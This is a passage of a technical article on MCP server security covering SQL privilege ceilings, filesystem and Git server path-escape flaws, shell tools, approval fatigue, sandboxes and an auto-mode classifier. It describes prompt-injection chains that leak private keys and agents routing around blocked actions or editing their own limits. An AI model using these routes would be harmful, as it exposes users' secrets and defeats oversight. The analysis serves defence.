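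A server limited to fixed report queries could not have sent `DROP TABLE` unless someone had taken it over. Ma and colleagues want to guard against a compromised server as well as a misled agent, so they put their check outside the server.

### A ceiling for each server process

MAP stands for MCP-Aware Privilege Enforcement. The person who deploys a server gives its process a ceiling, which is the highest class of operation its job requires. Write *P(p)* for the ceiling of process *p*, and *C(m)* for the class of a database message *m*. With the classes in the order READONLY < WRITE < ADMIN, the rule is:

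*allow(p, m) if and only if C(m) ≤ P(p)*

A reporting server with a READONLY ceiling can send `SELECT` but not `INSERT` or `DROP`, even when it logs in to the database as root. The database still applies its own permissions to any statement MAP allows.

To apply the rule, MAP must be able to identify the process sending a message, read the SQL in the message, and block it. Checks placed elsewhere lack one of these abilities. A filter inside the server fails if an attacker controls the server. A proxy in front of the database can read and block SQL, but if several servers share an account, it cannot reliably identify which one sent a query. Linux's usual access controls can identify the process and block its connections, but they do not ordinarily distinguish a `SELECT` from a `DROP`.

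MAP therefore runs inside the Linux kernel, at the point where a process hands over data to be sent. It identifies a server by details such as the program's name, its command-line arguments and the user account that started it. When a monitored server sends a message to a database, MAP finds the SQL in it, copies at most 512 bytes and reads the first keyword. If the keyword's class is above the ceiling, the send fails with an error to the server, and the database receives nothing. If MAP can decode a query message but doesn't recognise its first keyword, it classes the keyword as ADMIN, so a server cannot get around its ceiling by using an obscure command.

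The researchers tested all three ceilings against eight kinds of statement in both MySQL and PostgreSQL, and MAP's decisions were all correct. In a further test, it assigned the expected class to all 2,000 queries. They then ran the 123 working servers under MAP without changing the servers' code, and the legitimate operations they tried still worked. When they repeated the attack on the analytics server with a READONLY ceiling, the report ran and the `DROP TABLE` failed.

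MAP's ceilings do little to restrict some servers. Of the 47 that requested root or its equivalent, 33 could run queries. The researchers gave 22 of these a WRITE ceiling. The other 11 had administrative operations in their code, so they received an ADMIN ceiling, under which MAP allows everything. A generic tool poses a similar problem because its code does not show which operations the user will need. The operator has to choose the ceiling based on what the server is meant to do, perhaps after running MAP in an audit mode that logs violations without blocking them.

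MAP added 28 microseconds (4.4%) to the mean time per query and 725 microseconds at the 99th percentile. Median throughput fell 13.6%, from 1,418 to 1,225 queries a second. The delay hardly matters to a developer waiting for a language model to write the next query, but the lost throughput could matter on a heavily used server.

### Which table, which rows, which statement

MAP does not decide which table a `SELECT` may read. Ma and colleagues leave that to the database's own permissions. A READONLY ceiling would have let the agent in the Supabase attack read the secret tokens, though it would have blocked the write that delivered them to the attacker.

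The classes are also only a rough guide to how much damage a statement can do. `TRUNCATE orders` and `DELETE FROM orders` with no condition both empty the orders table, but the first belongs to the ADMIN class and the second to the WRITE class. A server with a WRITE ceiling can therefore delete every row in the shop's database, though it can't remove the tables themselves.

Reading only the first keyword creates another gap. PostgreSQL accepts several statements in one message if semicolons separate them, so under MAP's rule a message that starts with `SELECT` and continues with `DROP TABLE` would count as a read. A `SELECT` can also call a stored function that changes data. The paper reports tests that varied the spacing and capitalization around the keywords, but none that covered either of these cases. The rule can also be too strict, since a harmless query that starts with `WITH` would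 count as ADMIN.

The prototype reads one type of query message for MySQL and one for PostgreSQL, and lets all other traffic through. PostgreSQL drivers use a different message format for prepared statements, so those would pass unchecked. Queries on an encrypted connection presumably would too, because the kernel handles only encrypted data. The prototype's designers could narrow these gaps, but for now an operator should not rely on MAP alone to contain a server that an attacker controls.

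The researchers also assume that MAP runs on a host shared by the MCP server and the database, and that the host's administrator can load programs into the kernel. Someone using a vendor-hosted server cannot load such programs. MAP does not restrict someone who copies a password from a public repository and connects from another computer.

### A separate account for each server

A simpler remedy is to give each server its own database account with only the permissions it needs. Ma and colleagues call this a strong baseline. The idea is not new; the MySQL manual tells administrators, "Do not grant more privileges than necessary."

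Some developers of generic tools pass this advice on. Glama's *MySQL Security Configuration* is a guide to the MySQL server whose code passes any query to the database. It tells users to create a dedicated account, never to connect as root, and to accept connections only from the same machine if the server runs there. It also provides ready-made grants for three levels of access: reading, reading and modifying, and a level that adds temporary tables. All three cover every table in the database, so even the read-only one lets the agent read everything. More usefully, the guide later suggests granting access to specific tables or columns and using views, which are stored queries that show only part of the data.

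The guide also suggests limits of 1,000 queries and 100 updates an hour. These would slow down an agent stuck in a loop, but they offer little protection against theft or sabotage, because a single `SELECT` can return a whole table and a single `DELETE` can empty one.

For the shop's delivery questions, the operator could create an account called `order_reader` and give it two columns of one table:

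```sql
GRANT SELECT (order_id, status) ON orders TO order_reader;
```

The table below shows what a standing approval of `execute_sql` would cover with this account and with the owner account. The rows for MAP assume that it classifies every statement correctly.

| Account and ceiling | What standing approval of `execute_sql` covers |
|---|---|
| Owner account | All 160 combinations of table and operation, plus altering or dropping tables |
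| Owner account with a WRITE ceiling | All 160 combinations |
| Owner account with a READONLY ceiling | Reading all 40 tables |
| `order_reader` | Reading the number and status of every order |

With `order_reader`, "always allow" grants about as much access as it does for the narrow `get_order_status` tool. The agent can still write its own SQL, for example to count delayed orders or list every order awaiting dispatch, so nobody has to write a tool for each question. The user does not need to understand each query to know that it cannot read an address.

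Someone with administrative rights has to create the account, write its grants, change the server's configuration and update the grants when the tables change. Many public servers make it easier to skip this work by accepting whatever connection string the user already has or recommending a powerful service credential. MAP is more useful where several servers share an account that is hard to split, because an operator can lower one server's ceiling without affecting the others. Where the operator can create accounts, the database's own grants are more precise and don't depend on guessing a statement's effect from its first word.

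However, a dedicated account gives everyone who uses the server the same permissions. If support staff and the finance department share a server, its account needs permission for both groups' work, so support staff can also query payments.

### Queries under the caller's own identity

Google's Cloud SQL service, which hosts MySQL and PostgreSQL databases, avoids that problem by running each query with the caller's own database privileges. The caller logs in through Identity and Access Management (IAM), Google's system for accounts and permissions. The service's generic `execute_sql` tool accepts any valid SQL statement, including commands that change tables or permissions, and one call can contain several statements. But if a support employee's database account cannot read the payments table, the employee's agent cannot read it through this tool either.

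The server then has no powerful account of its own for a less privileged caller to exploit, which deals with the confused deputy problem. This does less against prompt injection, because injected instructions run with the permissions of the person using the agent. If a database administrator asks an agent to summarise customer messages, an instruction injected into one of them could expose everything the administrator can access.

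The agent's identity therefore matters. Google Cloud recommends creating a separate identity for agents so that administrators can control and monitor their access. This combines the two remedies, since the agent has its own account with grants for its own job and does not inherit all the permissions of the person who started it.

The limit holds only if the agent cannot change its own permissions. On its main address, the Cloud SQL server also offers `update_user`, which can grant database roles. The setup guide lists two IAM roles that let a caller run SQL, Cloud SQL Studio User and Cloud SQL Admin. The Admin role also lets the caller update database users. For callers who get authentication errors and lack the right database roles, the `execute_sql` reference page suggests granting those roles with `update_user`, and gives the powerful `cloudsqlsuperuser` role as an example. An agent with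 the Admin role that followed this advice could remove the restriction protecting the database.

Google Cloud's *Execute SQL statements using the Cloud SQL Data API* gives more cautious instructions for the same kind of access. It tells administrators to assign custom roles with the least privileges, and to use `cloudsqlsuperuser` only until they have created them. Its sample configuration still assigns `cloudsqlsuperuser`, with a comment that smaller roles can replace it.

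Operators can also withhold `update_user` from the agent. Google Cloud's *Cloud SQL Admin API for MCP* lists separate addresses for different groups of tools. The address for running queries offers only `execute_sql` and a tool that checks the status of long operations. SQL also has commands for granting permissions, so the agent's database account must lack the right to use them.

A newer version of the `execute_sql` reference adds two optional arguments, one for the name of a database user and the other for the location of that user's stored password. With them, a call can run under an ordinary database account instead of the caller's own. The model writes these arguments along with the SQL, so it can run queries under any account whose password the caller has permission to use. Google's advice to let each user access only specific stored passwords therefore also helps limit what the tool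 can do.

Google also offers a control that applies to whole tools. Google Cloud's *Prevent read-write MCP tool use* describes a policy that rejects any call to a tool without a read-only label. Google's servers enforce the policy regardless of what the user or host has approved, and Google labels its own tools, so the policy does not depend on a third party's annotations. Like a READONLY ceiling in MAP, it is a coarse limit set outside the agent. It blocks `execute_sql` even when the query is a harmless `SELECT`, and it allows `execute_sql_readonly` to read every table that the database account used for the call can read. To keep an agent with that tool from reading the payments table, an administrator still has to deny the account access to that table.

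## File and Git servers that reach beyond their folder

A file server on the user's machine normally runs under the user's own login, which gives it permission to open tax returns, saved passwords and the private keys used to log in to other computers. It rarely has a separate account with narrow permissions, which an operator can set up for a database server.

The approval prompt for a file tool shows little more than a name and a path. If the user approves `read_file` on `notes.txt`, the server receives a request for that file, but the operating system doesn't enforce the approval and would let the same process open any other file the user can open. Model Context Protocol's *Connect to local MCP servers*, a guide for new users, says that every action needs the user's explicit approval, but also warns that the server "can perform any file operations you can perform manually". Turning on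 a host's sandbox may not prevent this. The one built into Claude Code confines only shell commands, and Anthropic says that local MCP servers run outside it "with your full access".

### Allowed directories

The guide's example is the Filesystem server, a reference server that reads, writes, moves and searches files. The user lists the folders it may touch in the command that starts it:

```
mcp-server-filesystem /home/ana/work /home/ana/Downloads
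```

The server compares each requested path with this list and refuses any path outside it. The model writes only the arguments of later calls, so it cannot change the list. But the server process keeps all the user's permissions, so the limit holds only if the server compares paths correctly.

In 2025, Elad Beber of the security company Cymulate reported two ways around this restriction. GitLab's *CVE-2025-53110* (2025), a numbered entry in a public catalogue of security flaws, describes how the server could accept a path that began with the same characters as an allowed folder. With the list above, a call could also have opened files in `/home/ana/work-private`. GitLab's *CVE-2025-53109* (2025) describes the other way, which used symbolic links, entries in one folder that point to something elsewhere. A link inside `work` could lead the server out of that folder, although the path in the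 approval prompt looked correct. Release 2025.7.1 fixed both flaws.

### Why roots did not confine anyone

The protocol's own way for a client to tell a server about folders was to send roots, which are `file://` addresses, typically for the project the user has open. According to the server's documentation, *Filesystem MCP Server*, roots were the recommended way to set its allowed directories, and roots from a client replaced the whole list given at launch.

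The Filesystem server enforced the roots it received, but other servers could ignore them. Model Context Protocol's *Roots* (2026) calls roots "informational guidance rather than an access-control mechanism" and says only that servers SHOULD respect them, as the Model Context Protocol specification had since 2024. Model Context Protocol's *client concepts* (2025) explains that the word is SHOULD rather than MUST because servers run code that the client cannot control, so no client could guarantee compliance. That page recommends roots for preventing accidents with trusted servers, and file permissions or a sandbox for security. It also introduces roots as defining "filesystem boundaries", which could easily lead someone who read only the introduction to think that roots restrict access.

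In *Deprecate Roots, Sampling, and Logging*, Van Gent (2026) argued for dropping the roots feature because few clients and servers supported it and a boundary that servers may ignore is not very useful. Van Gent added that removal slightly improves security, because roots reveal the layout of the user's disk to servers. The July 2026 specification deprecated the feature but keeps it for at least another year. According to Model Context Protocol's *Provide roots*, part of the documentation for the official TypeScript library, "nothing replaces it" and developers should give the server its paths directly.

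A file or Git server can get its allowed folder from its configuration or from the arguments of a tool call. A person writes the configuration before the agent has read anything, but the model writes the arguments, possibly after reading a malicious instruction. A folder named in the arguments therefore does not restrict the server. Only a folder set in the configuration can confine the server, as many users probably assumed roots did, and only if the server checks each path against it.

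### When a tool exceeds its scope

*My Credentials, Please* (Huang, Tang and colleagues, 2026) investigated how often servers from nine registries fail to make that check. The study first needed a definition of excess, since some tools are meant to read any file.

They compare two sets of file accesses. One is the tool's reach, counting only the arguments an attacker could steer through content the agent reads. The other, *B(t, d)*, is the access that tool *t* can justify in deployment *d*. The justification comes from the tool's name, description and schema, together with the launch settings, the folder the server is supposed to work in and the files it needs in order to run. A tool exceeds its scope when:

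*reach(t) ⊄ B(t, d)*

An attacker can cause at least one file access that the tool's description and deployment don't justify. The researchers call this "filesystem capability laundering" because a tool with a harmless-sounding description does something nobody would expect of it.

Suppose two tools can both open every file in Ana's home folder. One is a general file reader that Ana has configured for the whole folder, so it has no excess scope. The other is supposed to work on a single code project, so its excess scope is everything in the home folder outside that project. The definition therefore identifies tools that can do more than their descriptions state, but not a generic execution tool whose description states its full power. An `execute_sql` tool described as running any SQL, for example, would have no excess scope, even under the shop's owner account.

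Deciding what file access a deployment justifies is the hard part. Huang and colleagues treat launch settings, documented workspace folders and the developer's own path checks as strong evidence. A storage folder written into the code is weaker evidence, because it shows where the developer meant files to go but does not stop them from going elsewhere. A tool's name alone is the weakest evidence. A tool called `read_build_log` presumably reads build logs, but the name does not identify which folders may contain them.

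The researchers looked for excess at three layers, which can overlap.

| Layer | What suggests a problem | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Server category | The server can use files although its category does not suggest it | A memory server that writes to disk |
| Tool contract | A tool's arguments can reach files outside its declared job | A Git tool that accepts a file from outside the repository |
| Defeated path check | The code has a check, but some paths get around it | The Filesystem server's comparison of opening characters |

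### A planted secret and three runs

The study's software, MCP-FSD, starts each server, lists its tools and screens the source code for places where a path argument reaches a file operation. It keeps the tools whose response could plausibly contain a file's text. For each one, a language model drafts the tool's proper boundary from its launch settings, path arguments and description. The software then widens that boundary to include files the code visibly needs, such as its libraries.

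Next, MCP-FSD puts a fake credential outside the boundary and a harmless file inside it. A language model tries different arguments until the tool returns the credential or the attempts run out. If an attack works, the software runs three tests:

1. It makes the malicious call without a sandbox. The response must contain the fake credential.
2. It makes an ordinary call inside a sandbox that enforces the boundary. The call must succeed.
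3. It repeats the malicious call inside the same sandbox. The credential must not appear.

The ordinary call matters because a sandbox that blocked everything would stop every leak but make the tool useless. If all three runs go as required, they show that the tool can leak the file and that the operating system can prevent the leak without breaking the tested operation.

All three runs, however, rely on the boundary inferred by the language model. If the model wrongly confined a general file reader to one folder, the reader would return the fake credential, open the harmless file normally and fail in the sandbox. Those results would count as a violation even though the reader had done nothing its description ruled out. Huang and colleagues acknowledge that they did not measure how accurate the boundaries are, and that a successful ordinary call does not prove that a boundary matches what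 the user authorised. They do require a reason, based on the tool's contract and deployment, why each target was out of bounds, so the evidence is stronger for a server with a configured folder than for one with only a suggestive name.

The tests also start with the malicious call already written, so they show what happens once an agent sends it but don't measure how often injected text would persuade an agent to send it.

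### From 21,097 listings to 150 confirmed instances

| Stage of the study | Number |
|---|---|
| Listings catalogued in nine registries | 21,097 |
| Local open-source servers the researchers tried to start | 7,222 |
| Servers triaged by function | 4,806 |
| Triaged servers with any sign of file access | 2,131 (44.3%) |
| Triaged servers with file access but no file-system category | 787 (16.4%) |
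| Vulnerable instances confirmed by the three runs | 150 |

The 787 servers are leads for further checking, and the 16.4% is not a measure of how many servers are vulnerable. A server that keeps facts between conversations has to store them somewhere, so saving a file may be legitimate. A language model also assigned both the categories and the signs of file access, and there were no independent labels to measure its errors against.

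The source-code screening raised far more alarms, with 10,304 separate findings across 2,818 of the 4,292 servers for which it returned results. The researchers labelled about 300 examples by hand for each of two classifiers and found that 99.5% of the tools flagged for exceeding their contract were flagged correctly, and 95.3% of the findings about defeated checks were correct. These figures measure how accurately the software classified code, not how many findings an attacker could exploit. Some findings concern web addresses and disclose no local file.

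About 62% of the screening findings involved checks that seemed possible to defeat, but only 38 of the 150 confirmed instances involved bypassing an explicit check in the code. Most of the others seem to have had no such check. A plain path was enough in 144 of the 150 instances, and the other six needed the path wrapped in a valid document of a type the tool could parse.

An instance is one tool tested with one policy, so the 150 instances may come from fewer than 150 servers. The researchers also chose which candidates to test, so the number can't be used as a rate for all MCP servers. Almost all the servers that ran were written for Node (which runs JavaScript) or Python, and one registry supplied 84% of those that started.

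The count could also be too low. For 136 instances the evidence was the planted text, and for the other 14 it was something else, such as a changed file. The study did not systematically test whether tools could create, alter or delete files outside their scope. It also did not search for chains in which one tool writes a file and another later reads it, and it did not test servers that needed unusual settings to start.

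The paper's abstract reports 13 security advisories. The results section describes them as findings sent to maintainers, with fixes or CVE numbers still pending at the cutoff, although it also lists two CVEs in Anthropic's Git server that already had fixes. Eleven of the 13 findings were based on something in the code or configuration, such as a faulty check. The other two depended on the scope implied by the tool's contract, so a maintainer could more easily dispute them.

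### Four flaws in Anthropic's Git server

Git records successive versions of the files in a folder, called a repository. Anthropic's Git server offers separate tools for its operations, such as `git_add` and `git_diff`. A designer trying to avoid a generic shell tool might well choose this approach. But GitLab's *Advisories for Pypi/Mcp-Server-Git package* lists four flaws that let these tools act outside the repository or change files they should not.

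| Tool | Expected effect | Additional effect before the fix | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| `git_init` | Create a repository in the workspace | Turn any folder open to the server into a repository | Anthropic removed the tool in version 2025.9.25 |
| Tools that take a repository path | Work on the repository set at launch | Work on other repositories open to the server | Path check in 2025.12.18 |
| `git_diff` and `git_checkout` | Compare or switch versions | Overwrite files | Argument check in 2025.12.18 |
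| `git_add` | Stage files from the repository | Stage files from outside it | Git's own command does the staging from 2026.1.14 |

Staging a file copies its contents into Git's store for the next saved version. The `git_add` tool took a repository path and a list of files, then passed the list to a programming library that did not check whether relative paths stayed inside the repository. An injected instruction could therefore make an agent stage a private key from elsewhere on the disk. A second tool, `git_diff_staged`, would then return the key's text as a list of changes.

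With per-call approval, the user would see both calls. The request to stage files would include the suspicious path, perhaps among several ordinary ones, but would not return the secret. The request that returned the secret would name only the repository, so a user who reviewed it alone would have no reason to refuse. The key could also leak if a developer committed and pushed the staged files.

Huang and colleagues ran their three tests on the unpatched version of `git_add`. Without a sandbox, the two calls returned the fake credential. Inside the sandbox, ordinary staging worked and the malicious attempt failed with a permission error. MITRE's record of the flaw, *CVE-2026-27735* (2026), listed no known exploitation in late February 2026.

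The `git_init` flaw is harder to catch with a check on each path. Once an agent had turned a folder of private keys into a repository, the other tools could stage and display the keys without leaving that repository. A check that compared each file with the repository named in the call would have approved every step. The server needed to reject the `git_init` call because the new repository lay outside the user's workspace. Anthropic instead removed the tool because it intended the server to work only on existing repositories. Huang and colleagues analysed this flaw from the source code and credit Yarden Porat with first reporting it.

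In the repository path flaw, the user had followed the documentation and started the server with an option restricting it to one repository, but the server did not check later requests against that setting. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Bugs Found in Official Anthropic Git MCP Server* cites research by the security startup Cyata showing that an attacker could direct the server to any directory on the system. The configuration is the safer of the two places to set a limit, but the limit gave no protection until the code enforced it.

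The overwriting flaw came from how command-line programs read their input. `git_diff` takes the name of a version to compare, but Git treats a value that begins with a hyphen as an option, and one option writes the output to a file of the caller's choosing. The server passed the value to Git unchecked, so a tool for viewing differences could overwrite a file, and a read-only label on it would have been wrong even if given in good faith.

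TechRadar's *Anthropic's official Git MCP server had some worrying security flaws* reports that attackers could also combine the flaws with other MCP tools to run code on the user's machine. A user who approved a Git server and a file-writing server separately would have seen no prompt about using them together.

### A narrow name with a wide argument

`git_add` looks much more like the shop's `get_order_status` than like `execute_sql`, because it has a specific name and performs one operation. But an order number is an integer that identifies one order, whereas a path is a string that can lead outside a folder, pass through a link or name any file on the disk. The natural schema for a list of files accepts all of these paths, so a tool named for a repository operation can reach any file the user's account can read.

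A standing approval of the unpatched `git_add` therefore permitted much more than a user would have expected. A cautious user can at least tell from the name `execute_sql` that the tool may be risky, but had good reason to think `git_add` was harmless. A gateway that allowed `git_add` by name would have permitted the same unexpected access.

The argument doesn't have to look like a path. In `mcp-architect`, another server that Huang and colleagues tested, a tool added a project identifier to the name of its storage folder. The schema showed the identifier as an ID field, much like `order_id`, but a specially chosen value made the tool write a file outside that folder.

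A tool's description can mislead users even when there is no attacker. *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* (Shi, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a tool described as converting a "local PDF file" to text, whose code uploads the file to an outside service. Another tool is described as saving generated code, but it also makes the saved file executable. Both tools do this on every call, and a user who read the arguments carefully would not find out.

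To confine a file tool to its permitted folder, a developer has to follow any links in each path and refuse the path if it leads outside that folder. The check must also hold at the moment of access, because someone could swap a link after the path is checked. Huang and colleagues note that the protocol's TypeScript library has no ready-made function for this, so each developer writes their own. They suggest adding one, which would help only developers who know they need the check.

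### Confining the server process

A sandbox works even if the server's author gets this wrong, as the third run in the study showed. Some hosts can already sandbox an MCP server. According to VS Code's *MCP configuration reference*, a user on macOS or Linux can sandbox each local server, list the folders it may write to and the web domains it may contact, and deny it access to others.

For reading, though, the settings offer only a list of forbidden folders. The example configuration forbids the folder that usually holds login keys, which would have blocked access to the best-known target of the Git flaws. But a secret in a folder the user forgot to list would stay readable. Hardy's objection to lists of sensitive files applies here too.

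When the sandbox is on, VS Code approves the server's tool calls automatically, on the grounds that the server now runs in a controlled environment. But VS Code's *Understand trust and safety for AI agents* says that "Sandboxing and approval answer different questions". Inside the sandbox, an agent could still delete everything in the workspace folder it is allowed to write to, which an approval prompt might have stopped. The two protections would work better together.

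Huang and colleagues propose that servers state a file scope for each tool in the `tools/list` response. The user could then see, before approving `git_add`, that it reads and writes one repository. The client would also enforce that scope, whereas with a read-only hint it has to trust the server. A tool would fail if it needed files outside its declared scope, and the user could refuse a tool that declared the whole disk.

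Enforcement would be awkward because an operating-system sandbox normally applies to a whole process, and a server runs all its tools in one process. If one tool needs the whole home folder and another needs a single repository, a shared sandbox has to give both tools access to the whole home folder. To limit each tool separately, the client would need to run them in separate processes, or the developer would have to split the server.

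*AgentBound* (2025) sets limits for the server as a whole. Each server comes with a manifest of the general kinds of access it needs, such as reading files. The user then consents to particular folders, for instance letting the server read a codebase but write only to its README file. An enforcement engine stops the run if the agent requests a kind of access not listed in the manifest. The system can therefore enforce what the user approves. But when the folders change with every run, the user has to consent every time, which brings back the stream of prompts that leads people to click "always allow".

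## Shell tools and what approving a command grants

A shell is the program behind a terminal window. It reads a command, starts the programs named in it and passes them their inputs. Some MCP servers give agents a shell tool, which takes a command as a string and runs it. Anthropic's Git tools reached outside their repository because of programming errors, but a shell tool can open every file and start every program available to the user's account even when it works as intended.

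### Desktop Commander and its guardrails

Desktop Commander is an open-source server that gives an agent a shell on the user's computer. It has about 6,000 stars on GitHub, according to the project's README as reproduced in TypingMind's *Desktop Commander*. Anthropic's *Desktop Commander*, the server's entry in a directory of add-ons for Claude, lists 24 tools and advertises "full command-line superpowers". Anthropic says it cannot verify that such tools work as intended or that they won't change.

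Most of the tools have narrow names, such as `read_file` and `move_file`. The main shell tools are `start_process`, which runs a command, and `interact_with_process`, which sends input to a program that is already running. The README's examples include running Python code on a sales file and keeping a login open on a remote server. The shell tools can therefore reach any other computer or cloud account that the user can log in to from this one.

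The developers offer several restrictions and are frank about their limits.

| Restriction | What it does | Limits the developers acknowledge |
|---|---|---|
| `allowedDirectories` | Confines the file tools to listed folders; an empty list allows every folder | Terminal commands can still reach files elsewhere |
| `blockedCommands` | Refuses the commands on a list | There are several ways around it |
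| Docker installation | Runs the server in a container, which sees only the folders the user shares with it | None; they recommend it to anyone who needs security |

Desktop Commander's *Security Policy* (2025) calls the built-in restrictions "guardrails to help the AI model" avoid actions the user did not intend. It adds that security is "not currently our top priority", because few users had asked for more of it. The developers took the same position later that year, after someone published a flaw in the folder check. NVD's *CVE-2025-11489 Detail*, an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, quotes them as saying that the restrictions were never "hardened security boundaries". The README's feature list now advertises a command blocklist "with bypass protection", although warnings further down still say that it can be bypassed. Someone who reads only the feature list could easily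 overestimate how much the blocklist protects them.

A guardrail of this kind can still prevent accidents, but the model can use the server's own `set_config_value` tool to change both lists. The developers warn that Claude may sometimes try to change `allowedDirectories` after running into a restriction, and they advise users to make configuration changes in a separate chat. But the tool remains available in the chat where the agent is working. The Filesystem server's folder list is safer in this respect because it is fixed at launch.

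The server's instructions also steer the model towards the shell. The description of `start_process`, which Glama's *start_process* reproduces, includes the instruction to use it "For ANY local file work". A user might approve `read_file` for a single folder and expect the agent to use that tool, but the agent may follow the description and read the same files with a shell command, which the folder list does not restrict.

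### Refusing other tools when the shell has approval

Write *U* for everything the user's account can read, change or send. A shell that runs under this account without a sandbox has a reach of practically all of *U*, and any other local tool *t* under the same account has a reach somewhere inside it. So:

*reach(shell) ∪ reach(t) = reach(shell)*

Adding or refusing *t* doesn't change what the agent can do. If a user always allows `start_process` but rejects a call to `write_file`, the agent can still write the file through `start_process`.

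This matters even when the agent is not under attack, because models often look for another route when one fails. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes an internal case in which Claude could not upload a report to a company drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead. An automated check blocked the attempt. A model may also look for another route when a tool call is refused, and a shell offers more alternatives than any other tool.

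Refusing a tool still matters when the tool has permissions that the user's account lacks. An example is a remote payments server with its own credentials, provided the account holds no other login to the same service. Refusals also matter if the shell runs in a sandbox or under an account with fewer permissions, because its reach is then smaller than *U*.

The Model Context Protocol maintainers point out that an unrestrained shell is equally dangerous whether it comes from an MCP server or is built into the host. They describe risk as a property of the whole session because users routinely combine tools from several servers. Installing a shell server can therefore undo the caution a user showed when approving other tools.

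### One command, three approvals

Claude Code has a built-in shell tool, Bash. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code*, Claude Code's original default mode requires the user to approve every file write and shell command. Suppose a developer at the online shop asks Claude Code to run `python count_orders.py`, a script that counts the day's orders. The developer could consent in three ways.

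| Consent | What it covers |
|---|---|
| Approval of this call | The command shown, once, including everything the script does |
| Standing approval of commands that begin with `python` | Every Python program the agent chooses to run |
| Standing approval of the tool | Every command |

A user learns less from the approval prompt for a shell command than from the one for a SQL query. The text of a query mostly determines what the database will do, but a shell command may only name a script, and the prompt doesn't show the script's contents. The command can also start other programs, which may start more, and no prompt shows what those programs do.

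A command pattern is an attempt to make a generic tool narrower. It limits standing approval to the effects of the commands that match it:

*reach(shell, p) = ⋃ E(shell, a), for every command a that matches pattern p*

This works well for a program that does one thing, such as a code formatter. It fails for an interpreter, which runs code in a language such as Python, because that code can do nearly anything the shell can. The second and third rows of the table therefore grant almost the same access, though the second looks much more cautious.

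Anthropic reports that, as of June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had created at least one rule allowing Bash commands. It adds that 5% allow any command and another 43% have interpreter rules that are "essentially equivalent in practice". It is unclear whether those two figures are shares of all active users or only of those with a rule. In the first case, nearly everyone who wrote a rule effectively allowed any command. In the second, about half did, or roughly a quarter of all active users.

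Other users skip the patterns. According to the same account, 62% have either clicked "don't ask again" for Bash or used the mode that bypasses permission checks, and a quarter of interactive sessions start in that mode.

In Claude Code's newer auto mode, a model reviews commands in place of the user. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that this mode keeps narrow rules but ignores broad ones, such as those that grant blanket shell access, allow interpreters by wildcard, or allow commands that run a project's own scripts. The company concedes that its list of dangerous patterns will always be incomplete.

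A host can offer patterns for its own shell tool because it can parse the argument as a command. With `start_process`, it sees only a string argument to a tool defined by someone else's server. The "always allow" choices in Snowflake's agent and VS Code apply to a whole MCP tool or server, so for an MCP shell there is no option between the first row of the table and the last.

### What a 97% approval rate proves

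Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts, according to Anthropic's August 2026 figures. The company reported 93% in March. It takes the high rate as a sign that many people approve prompts by reflex, though it acknowledges that most prompts are probably for safe, routine commands.

The rate alone cannot separate reflex from care. Let *d* be the share of prompts that are dangerous, *c* the share of dangerous prompts that users refuse, and *f* the share of harmless prompts they refuse:

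*approval rate = (1 − d)(1 − f) + d(1 − c)*

When dangerous commands are rare, the approval rate barely measures how well users spot them. If one prompt in a thousand is dangerous, users who refuse every dangerous command and 2.9% of harmless ones approve 97% of prompts, but so do users who refuse only one dangerous command in seven and 3.0% of harmless ones. For the same reason, the approval rate could have risen from 93% to 97% because users became less attentive or because agents proposed fewer objectionable commands.

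Anthropic also reports that users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, compared with 3% of commands. This shows that people are willing to refuse the agent. But a user may reject a plan because it takes the wrong approach or leaves something out, so the gap does not measure how carelessly users review commands.

### A dangerous command in front of 1,053 testers

Measuring *c* directly requires showing people a command known to be dangerous. Anthropic did this with 1,053 paid professional testers, hired through a research vendor for a coding study. They worked in a test environment and knew they were being evaluated, but not which behaviour mattered. Partway through each session, a clearly dangerous command replaced the text of one permission prompt, and the vendor recorded whether the tester approved it. Only the displayed text changed, so approving the command did no harm.

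The testers refused 143 of the 1,053 commands, or 13.6%. Anthropic ran the classifier behind auto mode on the same commands, and it blocked 937, or 89%. The company also published the number of commands that only one of the two stopped, and the rest of this table follows from the totals.

| | Classifier blocked | Classifier allowed |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 |

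This is much stronger evidence of inattention than the approval rate, because every approval in the test was a mistake. The exact figure may not carry over to ordinary work. People have more to lose on their own computers and might read more carefully. But these testers knew they were being evaluated, and a command swapped into the prompt at random may have stood out more than one that fits the task.

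Testers refused only about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session, and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Fatigue is the obvious explanation for the drop, but some of it may arise because people who click quickly get through more prompts. Anthropic does not report whether it allowed for this.

Anthropic ran the study to support a change to its own product, so an independent replication would be useful. Still, per-call approval of shell commands would look like a dependable barrier only if the result were very far off.

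### Fewer prompts inside a sandbox

If people review badly because they see too many prompts, a sandbox should help by making most prompts unnecessary. In Claude Code's sandbox, described in Anthropic's *Sandboxing*, the user sets the folders and network addresses that shell commands may use, the operating system enforces those limits, and the agent works inside them without asking about each command. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) reports that sandboxing cut permission prompts by 84% in the company's internal use.

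At that rate, 100 prompts in a session would drop to 16, so the user would never reach the fiftieth, after which the testers did worst. But the testers missed most dangerous commands even at the start, so the larger benefit probably comes from the sandbox's limits, which hold even when nobody is paying attention.

The limits have to cover both files and the network. Anthropic notes that without network limits, a hijacked agent could send out the user's login keys, and without file limits, it could escape the sandbox and regain network access. Desktop Commander's Docker installation falls short of the "complete isolation" it promises. The README's sample commands share the user's Desktop and Documents folders with the container and don't limit its network connections. An agent couldn't reach the rest of the disk, but it could send files from those folders anywhere.

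Data can also leak through approved network routes. InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* (2026) reports that the company revised its designs partly because of failures along permitted routes out of the sandbox. It still argues for fixed limits on files, network and execution rather than relying on prompts alone.

Claude Code's sandbox does not cover local MCP servers. A developer who turns it on and then adds Desktop Commander with the one-line command in its README has two shells on the same machine, only one of which is sandboxed. A command that the sandbox blocks may still run through Desktop Commander.

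### A classifier in the user's place

In August 2026, Anthropic began making auto mode the default for new Claude Code sessions on its Pro, Max and Team plans. Routine actions, such as reading files or editing those in the project, run without a check. A classifier allows or blocks most other actions, including shell commands and calls to outside tools. It receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls but not the results of those calls, so instructions hidden in a file or web page do not reach it directly. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user for approval.

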